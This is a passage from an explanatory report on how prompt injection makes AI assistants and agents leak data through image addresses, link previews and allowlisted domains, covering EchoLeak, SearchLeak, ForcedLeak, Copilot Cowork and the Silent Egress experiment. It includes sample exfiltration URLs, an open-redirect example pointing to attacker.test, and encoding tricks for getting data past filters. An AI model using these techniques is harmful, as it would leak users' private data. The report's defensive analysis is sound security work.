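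The damage is uncertain. Koi guessed that about 300 organisations were sending the developer 3,000 to 15,000 emails a day, based on 1,500 downloads a week and an assumed 20 per cent in active use. The Hacker News (2025) reports 1,643 downloads in total and a first upload on 15 September. ThaiCERT's *Researchers Discover First Malicious MCP Server in Rogue Postmark-MCP Package* (2025) dates the malicious version to 17 September, so the harmless versions were available for about two days, although Koi's account suggests trust built up over months. The developer later deleted the package from npm, but it stayed on users' machines. Postmark told users to uninstall it, check their email logs and consider changing any passwords they had sent by email.

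### A message to the user's own account

Copilot Cowork is an agent that works with a user's mail, calendar, files and Teams chats in Microsoft 365. Before it sends an email, it shows the user a preview and waits for approval. Microsoft's *Application card* calls this approval system the product's "primary safety mechanism". According to Microsoft's *Explore how Cowork works*, scheduling a meeting or sharing a document typically requires approval too.

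Microsoft's *Copilot Cowork common questions* explains that users can also choose "Don't ask again", which skips the prompt for similar actions during the rest of the conversation. Because the permission applies to a type of action, a user who chose it while sending the report to Dana might see no prompt if an injected instruction later made the agent email a stranger. PromptArmor advises organisations to prohibit the option for sending email, among other actions. A narrower remedy would be to keep prompting for new recipients.

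Microsoft (2026) is also developing an approval setting for Copilot Studio, its product for building agents. Builders will be able to require approval before an agent uses a chosen tool, such as one that sends email, regardless of the agent's instructions.

PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed that Cowork sent messages to the user's own account without asking for approval, and that users had no setting to change this. The exception seems reasonable because nobody else receives the message, and a recipient check would pass it for the same reason. In an earlier post on a Microsoft forum, *Cowork can't send emails?*, VirginiaH1 (2026) reported that Cowork could email only her own address because the approval prompt for other recipients never appeared. Cowork told her that emails to herself "appear to be auto-approved". An assistant's account of its own software is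 weak evidence, but this one agrees with PromptArmor's tests.

PromptArmor's demonstration used Teams, though the researchers report the same gap for email. They hid instructions in a skill file, a set of directions that a user can add to Cowork. When the user asked for a review of the week's work, Cowork collected links that let anyone download recent files without logging in. It put these links into the addresses of images on an attacker's site and sent the images to the user in a Teams message. When the user opened the message, Teams requested the images and so sent the links to the attacker. The full attack worked in all five trials.

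In May 2026, Willison attributed the leak to how the messages were displayed. PromptArmor describes it as a risk in the product's design rather than a specific bug. PromptArmor suggests that administrators block file downloads from sensitive sites, which would make the stolen links useless but would also prevent users from downloading, printing or syncing those files. A check on outgoing messages could stop the leak earlier, but it would have to treat each image address in the message as a destination, as well as the recipient's mailbox.

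## Why can an image or a link preview leak data without a click?

Images and link previews can leak data without a click because software requests their addresses automatically. In the Cowork demonstration, the requests went out when the user opened a Teams message. In an ordinary chat window, the image appears in the answer to the user's question, so the user doesn't have to open a message.

### From an answer to a web request

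A language model produces plain text. Most chat interfaces let that text contain Markdown, a simple notation for headings, links and images, and convert it into HTML, the language of web pages. With the harmless phrase used earlier, an image makes its request in four steps:

1. The model writes `![chart](https://example.com/log.png?q=blue+umbrella)` in its answer.
2. The interface converts this into the HTML tag `<img src="https://example.com/log.png?q=blue+umbrella">`.
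3. The browser reads the tag and requests the address so that it can display the picture.
4. The server at `example.com` records the address in its log, including "blue umbrella".

In an attack, injected instructions make the model replace the phrase with something from the conversation or from a document it has read. The browser makes the request, so an assistant can leak data this way even if it has no web access or other tool for sending data.

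The answer can look normal because the server can return any image. Willison (2023), in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, reports that the engineer Roman Samoilenko demonstrated the leak on ChatGPT with a one-pixel image. A user would be unlikely to notice a single pixel under an otherwise helpful answer. The image can also appear well after the injection. In a test on Microsoft's Bing Chat, it appeared two turns after the chatbot had read the malicious text, when a user would have had little reason to connect the two.

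The request goes out whenever a program displays the answer, even if that program isn't the chat window. Red Hot Cyber's *OpenAI API Logs Vulnerability Exposed* (2026) describes a leak that PromptArmor reported in OpenAI's log viewer, where developers read the answers their applications receive. Even if the application blocked a malicious answer from reaching its user, the viewer displayed the answer's Markdown images, so the data leaked when a developer opened the log.

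### The reports of 2023

Samoilenko found the flaw in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023. Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, found it independently a few days later (*ChatGPT Plugins*). In Samoilenko's version, a website added instructions to any text a visitor copied, and the visitor then pasted both into ChatGPT. SecurityWeek reports that the attack also worked when a user asked ChatGPT to summarise a malicious web page.

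Rehberger reported the flaw to OpenAI in early April, but OpenAI decided not to fix it.

On 8 April he reported the same flaw in Bing Chat, which could read the web page its user was viewing. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* explains that a comment or an advertisement on the page was enough to steal other text from it. Microsoft told him on 15 June that it had put a fix in place. His earlier tests no longer worked, and Bing Chat now had a Content Security Policy that let the browser load images from only four Bing domains. He could not tell whether Microsoft had changed anything else.

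Rehberger reported to Anthropic on 12 July that a file uploaded to its chatbot Claude could trigger the leak, and the case was closed two weeks later, on 26 July. Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* says that Claude then showed a placeholder instead of loading the image automatically, and the user had to click "Show Image" to see it.

OpenAI introduced its first defense in December 2023, more than eight months after Rehberger's report. ChatGPT's web version began checking with an OpenAI server that an image address was safe before loading it. The iPhone app did not yet have this check, so the original attack still worked there. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* shows that the web version could still leak small amounts of data. The delay probably had little to do with the technical work, since Anthropic found a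 fix quickly.

### The same flaw in newer products

GitHub Copilot Chat, a programming assistant that can read the code open in a developer's editor, turned out to have the flaw in June 2024. Instructions hidden in the code could make it display an image whose address contained private data. GitHub fixed this by stopping the assistant from displaying images from untrusted domains.

By then the list of affected products also included Google Bard, Writer.com, Amazon Q and Google NotebookLM. Willison explains in *GitHub Copilot Chat* why the problem kept recurring. If a chat interface already handles private data and untrusted content, displaying Markdown images adds the third condition for theft, a way to send data out. Developers who add image support may not realize this. Mistral's chatbot Le Chat had the same problem later in 2024, and Willison (2024) reports in *This prompt can make an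 AI chatbot identify and extract personal details* that Mistral restricted Markdown images in response.

New cases were still appearing in 2026, about three years after OpenAI first heard of the flaw in ChatGPT. The security firm Rapid7 describes one in the macOS desktop app for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The app loaded remote images automatically, so instructions injected into a connected tool's results could leak source code or API keys, the passwords that programs use to identify themselves. Rapid7 knows of no real attacks. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* demonstrates the risk with a malicious email that makes Codex leak the full contents of the user's other emails.

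PromptArmor also found that Rovo, an agent for Atlassian's workplace software, displays Markdown images in its answers. According to PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls*, the firm reported its findings on 23 May 2026, received a case number and thanks, and heard nothing for more than two months. Rovo was still vulnerable when PromptArmor published in August.

### How a Content Security Policy works

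A web server can send a Content Security Policy (CSP) along with a page. The policy lists, for each type of resource, the places from which the browser may load it. A rule for images could look like this:

`Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' images.example.com`

Here `img-src` applies the rule to images, `'self'` stands for the page's own site, and `images.example.com` is one other permitted host. If an answer contains an image from anywhere else, the browser doesn't send the request.

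The browser applies the policy to the page itself, regardless of the attacker's wording or the notation the model used for the image. The policy is also a second barrier if the chat interface has its own filter and it misses a tag. Anyone can read the policy, so Rehberger could see which domains Bing Chat permitted, but he could only guess how OpenAI's server decided that an address was safe.

A CSP covers only the page it comes with. A phone app that displays the answer without a browser page and a server that fetches images each need their own rule. A list of permitted hosts also doesn't control what the rest of an address contains, so data can still leave through a permitted site that stores or forwards what it receives. The EchoLeak and SearchLeak attacks on AI assistants exploited this weakness.

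### Why a filter must act before the answer appears

Chat assistants usually display an answer while the model is still writing it. A browser requests an image as soon as its tag is on the page, so a filter that waits for the complete answer can remove the image only after the request has been sent.

GitLab, a service for storing and reviewing code, had a problem of this kind with its AI assistant, Duo. Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft*, published in May 2025, shows how an outsider could hide instructions in a public project, for example in a comment, the code or the description of a proposed change. Duo could read everything its user could read. When someone with access to a private project asked Duo about the public one, Duo followed the hidden instructions, collected private code and put an encoded copy into an image address.

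The researchers noticed that the formatting of Duo's answers changed line by line as the text arrived. The interface was converting each part into HTML before the rest of the answer had arrived. This is risky because the meaning of a line depends on its surroundings. An image tag inside a block of sample code is displayed as text, but outside one, the browser loads the image. The researchers got Duo to write an image tag in HTML instead of Markdown, and the browser loaded the image.

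Duo filtered its answers with DOMPurify, a widely used library for cleaning HTML. DOMPurify is mainly meant to remove code that would run in the browser. It leaves image tags in place by default, so it would probably have let this tag through even if it had examined the complete answer first. The filter's settings seem at least as important as the early display, which Legit Security emphasises.

Legit Security reported the flaw on 12 February 2025. By the time it published its findings, GitLab had stopped Duo from displaying images and forms that point to sites outside `gitlab.com`.

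An interface can display answers as they arrive if it holds back each image until the address is complete and a filter has approved it. The delay is short because most addresses are no longer than a line or two. The filter should examine the HTML because the model's text can include an image in several ways. In EchoLeak, a filter in Microsoft 365 Copilot missed a form of Markdown that gives the address separately from the image, according to *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data*, an unsigned blog post on trackr.live. A CSP avoids the timing problem because the browser checks it before each request.

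Approval prompts can also come too late. PromptArmor's *Notion AI* reported in January 2026 that Notion, a program for shared documents, saved its assistant's edits before the user had approved them, so an edit could leak data while the user was still deciding whether to accept it. The report had first gone to an outside company that screens security reports for Notion. Notion quickly released a fix once it learned of the problem.

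### Link previews

An assistant that answers through a messaging app can leak data by posting a link, because the app opens the link to create a preview. If the messaging company's servers make the request, a CSP in the user's browser has no effect on it.

Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* explains that Slack's servers have to fetch every address in a message to find out what kind of content it leads to. By default, Slack previews links in messages from both apps and people.

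Rehberger warned about this in August 2024, in Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*. He showed how to prevent it with two settings that a program can include when it posts a message to Slack. `unfurl_links` controls previews of text pages, and `unfurl_media` controls previews of images, video and audio. Slack's documentation tells developers to set both to `false` if they don't want Slack to request the address. If only one is off, Slack presumably still has to open the link to find out which setting applies.

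The settings apply to one message at a time, so the software that posts messages has to include them in each one. An MCP server for Slack that Anthropic had published as an example for developers did not include them. In Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory*, Rehberger considers an assistant that is allowed to post only to one private channel. Its user might well let it post without asking for approval, since only colleagues can read the channel. But Slack's servers still open any link in the message, which sends the data to an outside site. A check on recipients would not catch the leak, because the channel is familiar.

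Rehberger reported the flaw on 27 May 2025. Anthropic archived the server two days later without fixing it, though he could not say whether his report prompted the archiving. People were still downloading the server more than 14,000 times a week. He suggests fixing the flaw by adding Slack's two settings to the functions that post messages and replies.

In February 2026, PromptArmor invited people to test their own combinations of agent and messaging app. Its test website recorded each preview request and the data in the requested address. Visitors could then report which agent had caused the request, or that their agent had not caused one. OpenClaw, an agent that people can talk to through messaging apps, leaked data on Telegram with its default settings. Apostol's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* also lists Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio, Slack and Discord among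 the affected platforms.

These results show that the leak works in several widely used apps, but they are weak evidence of how common it is, because volunteers chose what to test and each result depends on how the developer or user had set up that pairing. For example, turning off link previews in Telegram could stop the same agent from leaking data this way.

PromptArmor has since ended the test, but the defaults have changed little. OpenClaw's documentation for version 2026.3.2, which came after the tests, still lists Telegram previews as on unless the user sets `linkPreview` to `false`. Slack also still creates previews by default, although its documentation now advises developers to consider turning them off for messages from a language model. PromptArmor would like messaging apps to offer a preview setting for each chat or channel, so people could turn previews off where an agent posts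 and keep them elsewhere.

### What the repairs stop and what they cost

| Repair | What it stops | What can still leak | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| No external images | Image requests from the chat interface to outside sites | Data in links that someone clicks or an app previews | Answers can't show pictures from the web |
| CSP for images | Browser requests for images from sites not on the list | Data sent through permitted sites, or from apps that the policy doesn't cover | Someone has to maintain the list, and other pictures don't load |
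| Fetching through a proxy | Direct contact between the user's device and the outside site | The private text, unless the proxy also checks the address | An extra server and some delay |
| Placeholder | Automatic loading | Data in any image the user chooses to open | A click for each image |
| Previews off | Preview requests for the agent's messages | Data in links that someone clicks | No title or picture under the agent's links |

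A proxy alone offers the least protection. It is a server that fetches the image for the user, so the outside site doesn't learn the user's IP address. But the proxy has to request the same URL, with the private text still in it. When Rehberger tested an image link in Slack, Slack's image proxy was one of three Slack programs that sent the data to the outside site. A proxy is still a convenient place to check image requests, because they all pass through it.

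A placeholder with a button to load the image still depends on the user's judgement. Rehberger accepted that Anthropic's fix stopped the automatic leak but called it imperfect. The button doesn't show what the image's address contains, and a hijacked assistant could describe the image as a chart the user needs to see.

For most chat products, blocking external images is probably worthwhile, because few answers need them. The product can still show pictures that it creates or stores itself. Microsoft's policy for Bing Chat allowed this, since the images that users asked the chatbot to create came from Bing's own domains. A shopping assistant that displays photographs from hundreds of shops would lose much more by blocking external images, so it would need to check each address instead.

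Turning previews off for an agent's messages costs less still. The links continue to work, and people's own messages can keep their previews.

### Signals in the address

A product that does load outside images or create previews can check each address first. A new domain is probably a stronger sign of a leak here than when a research agent opens a page, because an answer about the user's own email rarely needs an image from a site that nobody in the organisation has contacted before.

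A long parameter in the address is another sign of a leak, because the address has to carry the stolen text. But many legitimate addresses are long too. A link to a private file may contain a long code that grants access to it, and advertisers add codes to track where visitors came from. A length limit would also miss short secrets such as passwords, and an attacker could split a longer text across several images. Rehberger therefore suggested limiting the number of images in one answer.

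Private text in the address is the strongest of these signs, if the check can recognise it. The check could compare the address with the emails and documents the agent has read in the session, and a match of several words would be hard to explain as coincidence. But the model can encode the text first. Base64, a common method, represents any data using letters, digits and a few symbols. It turns `blue umbrella` into:

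`Ymx1ZSB1bWJyZWxsYQ==`

A search for "umbrella" would not find the encoded text. A check can decode base64, but an attacker can choose another encoding, or ask the model for a summary that shares few words with the original. *Is Perplexity Comet Safe?* (Gispan, 2025) reports that simple encoding was enough to get a user's data past the exfiltration checks in Comet, Perplexity's AI browser. That leak used a different kind of web request, but an image address can contain the same encoded text.

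In the earlier illustration, the combined check for private text and a new destination caught 85.5 of every 100 hijacks. If attackers encoded the text so that the check recognised it in only 10 per cent of hijacks, the check would catch only 9.5 of every 100 and raise about as many false alarms as before.

Looking for encoded text isn't enough either. Legitimate sites use encoded parameters, and the data that SearchLeak sent out was plain text.

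As with email recipients, a check can look at where the address came from instead of interpreting the content. Any part of an address that the model composed may contain private data. If the model copied the whole address from a page that already existed, it can't contain text from the user's mailbox, though it may still be harmful in other ways. The Hacker News (2026) describes research by Permiso Security in which ChatGPT automatically loaded images from a web page it had just summarised and showed the page's links as clickable. Permiso's concern was phishing, since the attacker's pictures and links appeared inside an answer that the user had reason to trust.

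## Can a list of approved domains keep data in?

A domain allowlist, which blocks requests to any domain not on it, can stop a hijacked agent from sending data straight to an attacker's server. It doesn't help if the attacker can receive data through a domain on the list. Researchers have found ways to get data out through allowed domains in products from Microsoft and Salesforce.

An allowlist contains only domains that someone has approved, so it is stricter than a history of past contacts, which an attacker may be able to add to.

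### Where to enforce a list

A list controls only the requests that pass through the software enforcing it.

| Place | What it controls | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Filter in the chat interface | Links and images in the assistant's answers | Requests by the agent's tools, and any notation the filter doesn't recognise |
| CSP in the browser | Images and other resources that the page loads | Clicked links, and requests by tools or servers |
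| The tool that fetches pages | Addresses that the agent opens with this tool | Images in answers, and requests by other tools |
| Network proxy | Web requests from the machines behind it | Requests from the assistant provider's own servers |

A network proxy is a server that relays an organisation's web traffic. If a connection is encrypted, the proxy normally sees only the host name, but it can still check that name against the list of approved domains. The organisation also has to block name lookups for unlisted domains, because a program can leak data through lookups alone, as the malicious program in the SolarWinds attack did.

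Google's assistant Gemini shows why restricting addresses in one place may not be enough. Google lists "Markdown sanitization and suspicious URL redaction" among Gemini's defences. The Hacker News (2025) explains that Gemini doesn't display images from outside addresses and removes links flagged by Safe Browsing, Google's service for identifying dangerous sites. The link check is a blocklist, which permits everything not already known to be bad, so a domain that an attacker has just registered might well pass. Checkmarx, a security firm, notes that the image rule protects Gemini from leaks that need no click, but not from links that the user clicks.

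These filters covered Gemini's answers but not its browsing tool. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* describes how an injected instruction made the tool request an address containing the user's saved information and location. The tool didn't check the destination properly or ask for confirmation. Google has since blocked this leak.

### How matching works

A check has to extract the host from an address and compare it with the entries on the list. Searching the whole address for an approved name isn't safe, because an attacker can put that name almost anywhere in it.

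| Address | Text search for `example.com` | Entry `example.com` | Entry `*.example.com` |
|---|---|---|---|
| `https://example.com/a` | Allows | Allows | Refuses |
| `https://cdn.example.com/a` | Allows | Refuses | Allows |
| `https://example.com.attacker.test/a` | Allows | Refuses | Refuses |
| `https://attacker.test/?from=example.com` | Allows | Refuses | Refuses |

The last two columns follow CSP rules, where the asterisk (a wildcard) matches any host under the domain but not the domain itself. Other products may treat wildcards differently, so administrators need to check before relying on one.

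Wildcards save work for a company with dozens of hosts, but they allow hosts that nobody has examined. If the domain's owner gives each customer a separate host, some of these may belong to strangers. Others may be old names that still point to a hosting account the company has given up, which an outsider can claim.

Redirects cause a different problem. A redirect is a reply from a server telling the program to open another address. Some sites have an open redirect, a page that forwards visitors to any address named in the link:

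`https://example.com/go?to=https://attacker.test/blue-umbrella`

If a tool checks only the first address, it approves `example.com` and then follows the redirect to `attacker.test`, whose server logs the phrase. To prevent this, developers can stop the tool from following redirects automatically and have it compare each new address with the list. Browsers already check redirects this way when they apply a CSP.

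Checking redirects doesn't help if the approved site fetches the second address itself. The browser or tool then makes only one request, to a domain on the list, and the site's server makes the other.

### The Silent Egress experiment

In *Silent Egress* (2026), Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay compared an allowlist with several other defences. They built an agent on qwen2.5:7b, a small open model with about 7 billion parameters. The user always asked the agent to summarise a web page. The software put the page's text, title and description directly into the model's input, which also contained made-up secrets such as an API key.

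In each attack page, the researchers put instructions for the agent to send the secret to a collection server they ran. They put these instructions in the page's body, title, description or link text. The agent reached the page either directly or through redirects, and the researchers instructed it to send the secret either whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs.

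The agent contacted the collection server in 423 runs, or 88.1 per cent. In 95 per cent of the successful attacks, the answer gave the user no sign of the attack, so checking only the answer would have missed nearly all of them. In 120 runs on harmless pages, the agent never contacted the server.

They then tested defences on the simplest version of the attack, which put the instructions in the page body, used no redirects and sent the secret in one piece. Each row of the table covers 30 runs.

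| Defence | Agent tried to send data | Request reached the server |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| System prompt forbidding the model to obey web content | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Delimiters marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| System prompt and delimiters | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 83.3% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 0% |
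| Filter for random-looking text | 0% | 0% |

The system prompt, which holds the developer's standing instructions to the model, works only if the model complies, as do the delimiters. The allowlist is ordinary code that runs when the agent tries to make a request. It permitted only exact matches to a fictional company's three hosts or `example.com`.

### Why the allowlist blocked everything

For this comparison, the researchers deliberately chose a collection domain that was clearly not on the list. Code that permits only four hosts will always refuse that domain, so the 30 runs mainly confirm that the code worked. The harder case is an attacker who can use a domain on the list. Lan and colleagues name compromised sites and open redirects as ways to do this, but they didn't test either against the list. The redirects in their study led the agent to the malicious page and weren't used to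 send the secret out.

The agent still tried to send the secret in every run with the allowlist. The allowlist blocked these attempts but didn't prevent the hijack, so an agent with an email tool could have tried emailing the secret next.

The figures for the two prompt-based defences are probably a poor guide to current models, though the allowlist result depends much less on the model. Qwen2.5 dates from 2024, and the version in this test was small even then. Newer models resisted every attempt in the test Anthropic commissioned. Lan and colleagues argue that stronger models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but they tested only one model. They call their success rates a lower bound because the attack texts were simple, yet they also describe the set-up as favourable to the attacker, with the secret in plain view and almost no system prompt.

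The experiment doesn't measure false alarms either, although the paper reports a false positive rate of zero. In the 120 harmless runs, it counted only requests to the attacker's server, which an agent reading an ordinary page had no reason to contact. For an allowlist, a false alarm is a legitimate request that it blocks. An agent restricted to those four hosts couldn't open most of the pages that users ask about, and the paper doesn't report how many ordinary tasks each defence disrupted.

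Some results for the other filters are hard to explain. One filter, called "redirect detection" in the paper, blocks numeric addresses, certain domain endings and paths containing words such as "collect". It doesn't follow redirects. The researchers had named the path on the collection server `/collect`, so the filter probably worked because it blocked that word.

The keyword filter triggered in only 23.3 per cent of runs. The paper suggests that the model had sometimes encoded or reworded the secret, but the filter should have let such requests through, and none reached the server. With the filter for random-looking text, the agent didn't try to send anything. The paper suggests that the model avoids such text when this filter is active, but doesn't explain how the model could know that it was.

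### Splitting the data across requests

In half of the 480 runs, the agent was instructed to send the secret in four separate requests. A fragment of four characters looks harmless by itself, and the attacker can join the fragments later. Splitting made the attack less reliable, probably because the agent had to keep track of the pieces over several steps. It contacted the server in 77 per cent of these runs, compared with 99 per cent of the runs in which it was told to send the secret whole.

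The paper measures how visible the leak is with Leak@k, the share of runs in which any part of the secret appears in the first k requests. For split secrets, it gives a Leak@1 of 26.3 per cent and a Leak@3 of 15.8 per cent. These figures can't both be right. The first request is also one of the first three, so any run that counts towards Leak@1 must count towards Leak@3:

`Leak@1 ≤ Leak@3`

The Leak@1 figure agrees with the paper's separate results for the eight kinds of split attack, so the mistake is probably in Leak@3.

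It's also unclear how often the attacker would have obtained the whole secret. The paper defines a completion rate, the share of runs in which all the pieces arrive, but its results don't include one. In its worked example, the four fragments contain only 16 of the key's 20 characters.

Lan and colleagues claim that splitting a secret into pieces gets it past simple content filters, but they tested the filters only on whole secrets. The claim is still plausible, because the filter for random-looking text ignores anything of ten characters or fewer. Splitting doesn't help against an allowlist, because every piece goes to the same unlisted domain.

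### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their mail, files and chats. In June 2025, Aim Security disclosed EchoLeak, an attack that began with an ordinary-looking email to an employee. When the employee later asked Copilot a question, the assistant could retrieve the email, follow the instructions in it and put sensitive information into the address of an image. The email never mentioned AI, which helped it get past a classifier that Microsoft used to detect prompt injection.

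Copilot's page also had a CSP for images. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) reproduces the policy, which has 29 different entries, 11 of them with wildcards. Bing Chat's policy in 2023 permitted only four domains.

The researchers searched the entries for one that would let data out, starting with `*.sharepoint.com`. SharePoint, Microsoft's service for company websites, gives each customer a separate host, so the wildcard also covered a site that an attacker had set up. A service on that site would fetch an outside address on request, but only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the site.

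`*.teams.microsoft.com` worked better for the attack. A preview service on that domain fetched any address included in a request, without requiring an invitation. The browser requested an image from Teams, which the policy allowed, and Teams then fetched the attacker's address, which contained the stolen data.

Willison (2025) describes the Teams address as an open redirect, but Ravia describes a server that makes the request itself. If it had been a redirect, the browser would have checked the second address against the policy and blocked it. Because the server made the request, the browser never received that address, so Microsoft had to fix the problem another way.

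Aim Security reported the attack in January 2025, and Microsoft fixed the vulnerability on its own servers in May. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reports that Microsoft found no evidence of real attacks and that Copilot now strips incoming outside content of embedded images and of links written in the notation the attack used.

### SearchLeak

A year later, the security firm Varonis found a similar way to get data out of the same product. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack that starts when an employee clicks a link to Microsoft's own site. The link contains a search query, which Copilot's enterprise search treated as instructions. Copilot then searched the employee's mailbox and put an email's subject line, which can contain a login code, into an image address.

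Microsoft had a filter that turned image tags into harmless text, but it ran only after the answer was finished, which was too late. GitLab Duo had the same problem.

The page's policy permitted requests to `*.bing.com`. When a user searches by image, Bing's server fetches the picture from an address the user provides. In the attack, this address belonged to the attacker and contained the subject line. The policy allowed the browser's request because it went to Bing.

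The policy that Ravia published in 2025 already included `*.bing.com`, so the EchoLeak repair left another service of the same kind still permitted. In July 2025, between the two disclosures, Microsoft (2025) listed "deterministic blocking" of known exfiltration methods among its defences. Cyber Security News reports that these methods included HTML image injection, which is how SearchLeak sent its data. Fixed rules like these also have to cover every permitted service that can pass data on.

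Microsoft fixed SearchLeak and rated it critical. Varonis advises companies to review their lists for any domain that fetches addresses supplied by users. Wildcards make a thorough review hard because each one may cover hundreds of hosts. A host can also gain new features after the review. Listing only hosts that serve stored images is safer. An entry in a CSP can also name a path, so a policy could permit one folder of images on a host without permitting its image search. However, a browser ignores the path after a redirect, so an open redirect elsewhere on the list could get around this limit.

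### ForcedLeak

The ForcedLeak attack, which the security firm Noma disclosed in September 2025, used an expired domain that was still on the list. It targeted Agentforce, a Salesforce product for building agents that work with customer records. Many companies that use Salesforce have a web form for prospective customers, and an attacker could submit hidden instructions through it. When an employee asked the agent about that entry, the agent collected other prospective customers' email addresses and put them into an image address.

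Salesforce's content security policy (CSP) would have blocked an image from an unknown site, but Willison notes that it still allowed `*.my-salesforce-cms.com` after the domain's registration had lapsed. Noma's researchers bought the domain, for $5 according to BeyondMachines, and used it to receive the data.

An allowlist records domain names but not who owns them, so it can become unsafe without anyone editing it. A check for new destinations might have caught this leak, because a newly re-registered domain usually has a recent registration date and few companies would have had recent traffic to it. It therefore makes sense to run the check on listed domains too. The check would probably have missed EchoLeak, where the only visible destination was Teams, and SearchLeak, where it was Bing, because both are familiar destinations at almost any company that uses Microsoft's products.

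Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025, Salesforce acknowledged it three days later, and new restrictions on agents took effect on 8 September, according to Security Affairs' *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection*. Salesforce also regained control of the domain, as Salesforce Ben reports, and corrected its CSP. Salesforce could have prevented the problem by routinely checking each domain's registration, or by removing domains from the policy when it stopped using them.

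### Salesforce's Trusted URLs

On 8 September, Salesforce extended its existing Trusted URLs feature to its agents. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* explains that an administrator must approve any external address before an agent may write or call it. Dataconomy (2025) reports that administrators can put the address either on the Trusted URLs list or in the agent's instructions. Salesforce now restricts the agent's output in addition to the images the browser may load, so one wrong entry in the CSP no longer necessarily causes a leak.

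The new rule also makes each customer responsible for its own list of approved domains. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* says that this agent removes URLs by default and shows administrators how to add exceptions. Its example is `https://docs.google.com`, which a company might want to allow for its own documents. But anyone can create a form on that host. Willison reports that a hijacked email assistant, Superhuman AI, sent private mail to an attacker's Google Form because the assistant's CSP allowed images from `docs.google.com`.

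PromptArmor recommends avoiding wildcards that cover sites where outsiders can post content, and blocking images from each trusted domain unless the agent needs to show them. An administrator could then let an agent link to Google documents without letting the browser load anything from Google automatically. Data could still leave if a user clicked a malicious link to the same host.

### Why OpenAI doesn't rely on a list

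One reason OpenAI gives for why a list of trusted sites isn't enough for ChatGPT is that many legitimate sites redirect visitors. A check on the first domain can therefore approve a request that ends up elsewhere. Checking every redirect solves most of this problem, but it doesn't solve the problem in EchoLeak and SearchLeak, where the approved service fetched the address itself.

The second reason is that people use far more of the web than a short list can cover, so a strict list would produce the frequent warnings that OpenAI wants to avoid. If a research agent opens 40 pages for a report and the list covers 90 per cent of them, the user gets four warnings.

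This second problem is harder to solve because a longer list also gives an attacker more to work with. Suppose that each entry has a 1 per cent chance of including a service that would pass data to a stranger, and that these chances are independent. The probability that a list of n entries has at least one such service is then:

`1 − 0.99^n`

If each entry on a list independently has a 1 per cent chance of having a gap that lets data out, the chance of at least one gap is about 4 per cent for the four domains in Bing Chat's old policy, 25 per cent for the 29 entries in Copilot's, and over 99 per cent for a list of 500. The 1 per cent is only an assumption, and a wildcard for a large company's services is surely riskier than a single host that stores pictures. But a list long enough for general browsing will almost certainly have a gap, so OpenAI checks exact addresses instead of domains.

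### Where a list works well

Neither objection matters much for an agent that needs only a few destinations. An agent that answers customers' questions from a company's help pages might need only the host that serves those pages, and one that files invoices might need only the accounting service. The company can examine these hosts properly, and the agent can refuse to contact any others without asking the user.

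A refused request is also a much stronger warning sign here than a new destination is for a general assistant. In the earlier illustration, 10 per cent of legitimate actions went to a new destination, and only about one alert in 10,500 was right. For the invoice agent, perhaps 1 in 100,000 legitimate actions would go to an unlisted host, for example because the accounting service had changed its address. With the other assumptions unchanged, ten million actions would produce 95 refusals from hijacks and about 100 from legitimate actions, so nearly half of the alerts would be right. The company should therefore record and investigate each refusal.

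A list of approved domains suits a coding agent less well, even though the agent may also need only a few domains. The agent often has to reach public code-sharing sites, where an attacker can open an account too.

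## How does a safe-URL check decide about one exact address?

A safe-URL check tests whether software may load one exact web address automatically. A domain allowlist depends on trust in a site, whereas a safe-URL check depends on whether the address itself could contain the user's secrets. Two addresses on the same site can therefore get different results:

`https://example.com/umbrellas`

`https://example.com/umbrellas?note=blue+umbrella`

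Suppose the first address is a public page, and "blue umbrella" in the second comes from the user's private mail. An allowlist that includes `example.com` permits both addresses. A safe-URL check should permit only the first, and it can do so even if nobody has examined the site.

OpenAI introduced such a check in ChatGPT in December 2023. Early versions made exceptions for trusted domains, and researchers found ways to send data out through those domains. The current version looks up the exact address in an index of public addresses.

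### What outsiders learned about url_safe

In the first version of the check, ChatGPT's web client, which runs in the user's browser, sent a request to an OpenAI service called `url_safe`. Rehberger tested it with an image address on his own site that had an email address in its parameters. The service replied `{"safe":false}`, according to Embrace The Red, and the browser didn't request the image.

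OpenAI did not publish its rules, so researchers tested addresses to work them out. Rehberger made a separate image address for each letter and digit, and nine of the 36 images loaded. He could not see why the image for "a" loaded and the one for "d" did not. He guessed that OpenAI might be looking addresses up in the index of Microsoft's search engine, Bing.

The security firm Imperva gives a different account in *From ChatBot To SpyBot*, perhaps because OpenAI had changed the rules by then. It found that `url_safe` approved any text, whether or not it was a web address, if it already appeared in what the user had supplied, including the standing instructions that users can save in ChatGPT.

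A search like this is looser than comparing whole addresses because it also matches parts of an address. If a user had pasted `https://example.com/umbrellas`, `https://example.com/umb` would pass too, and an attacker could use the shortened forms as a code.

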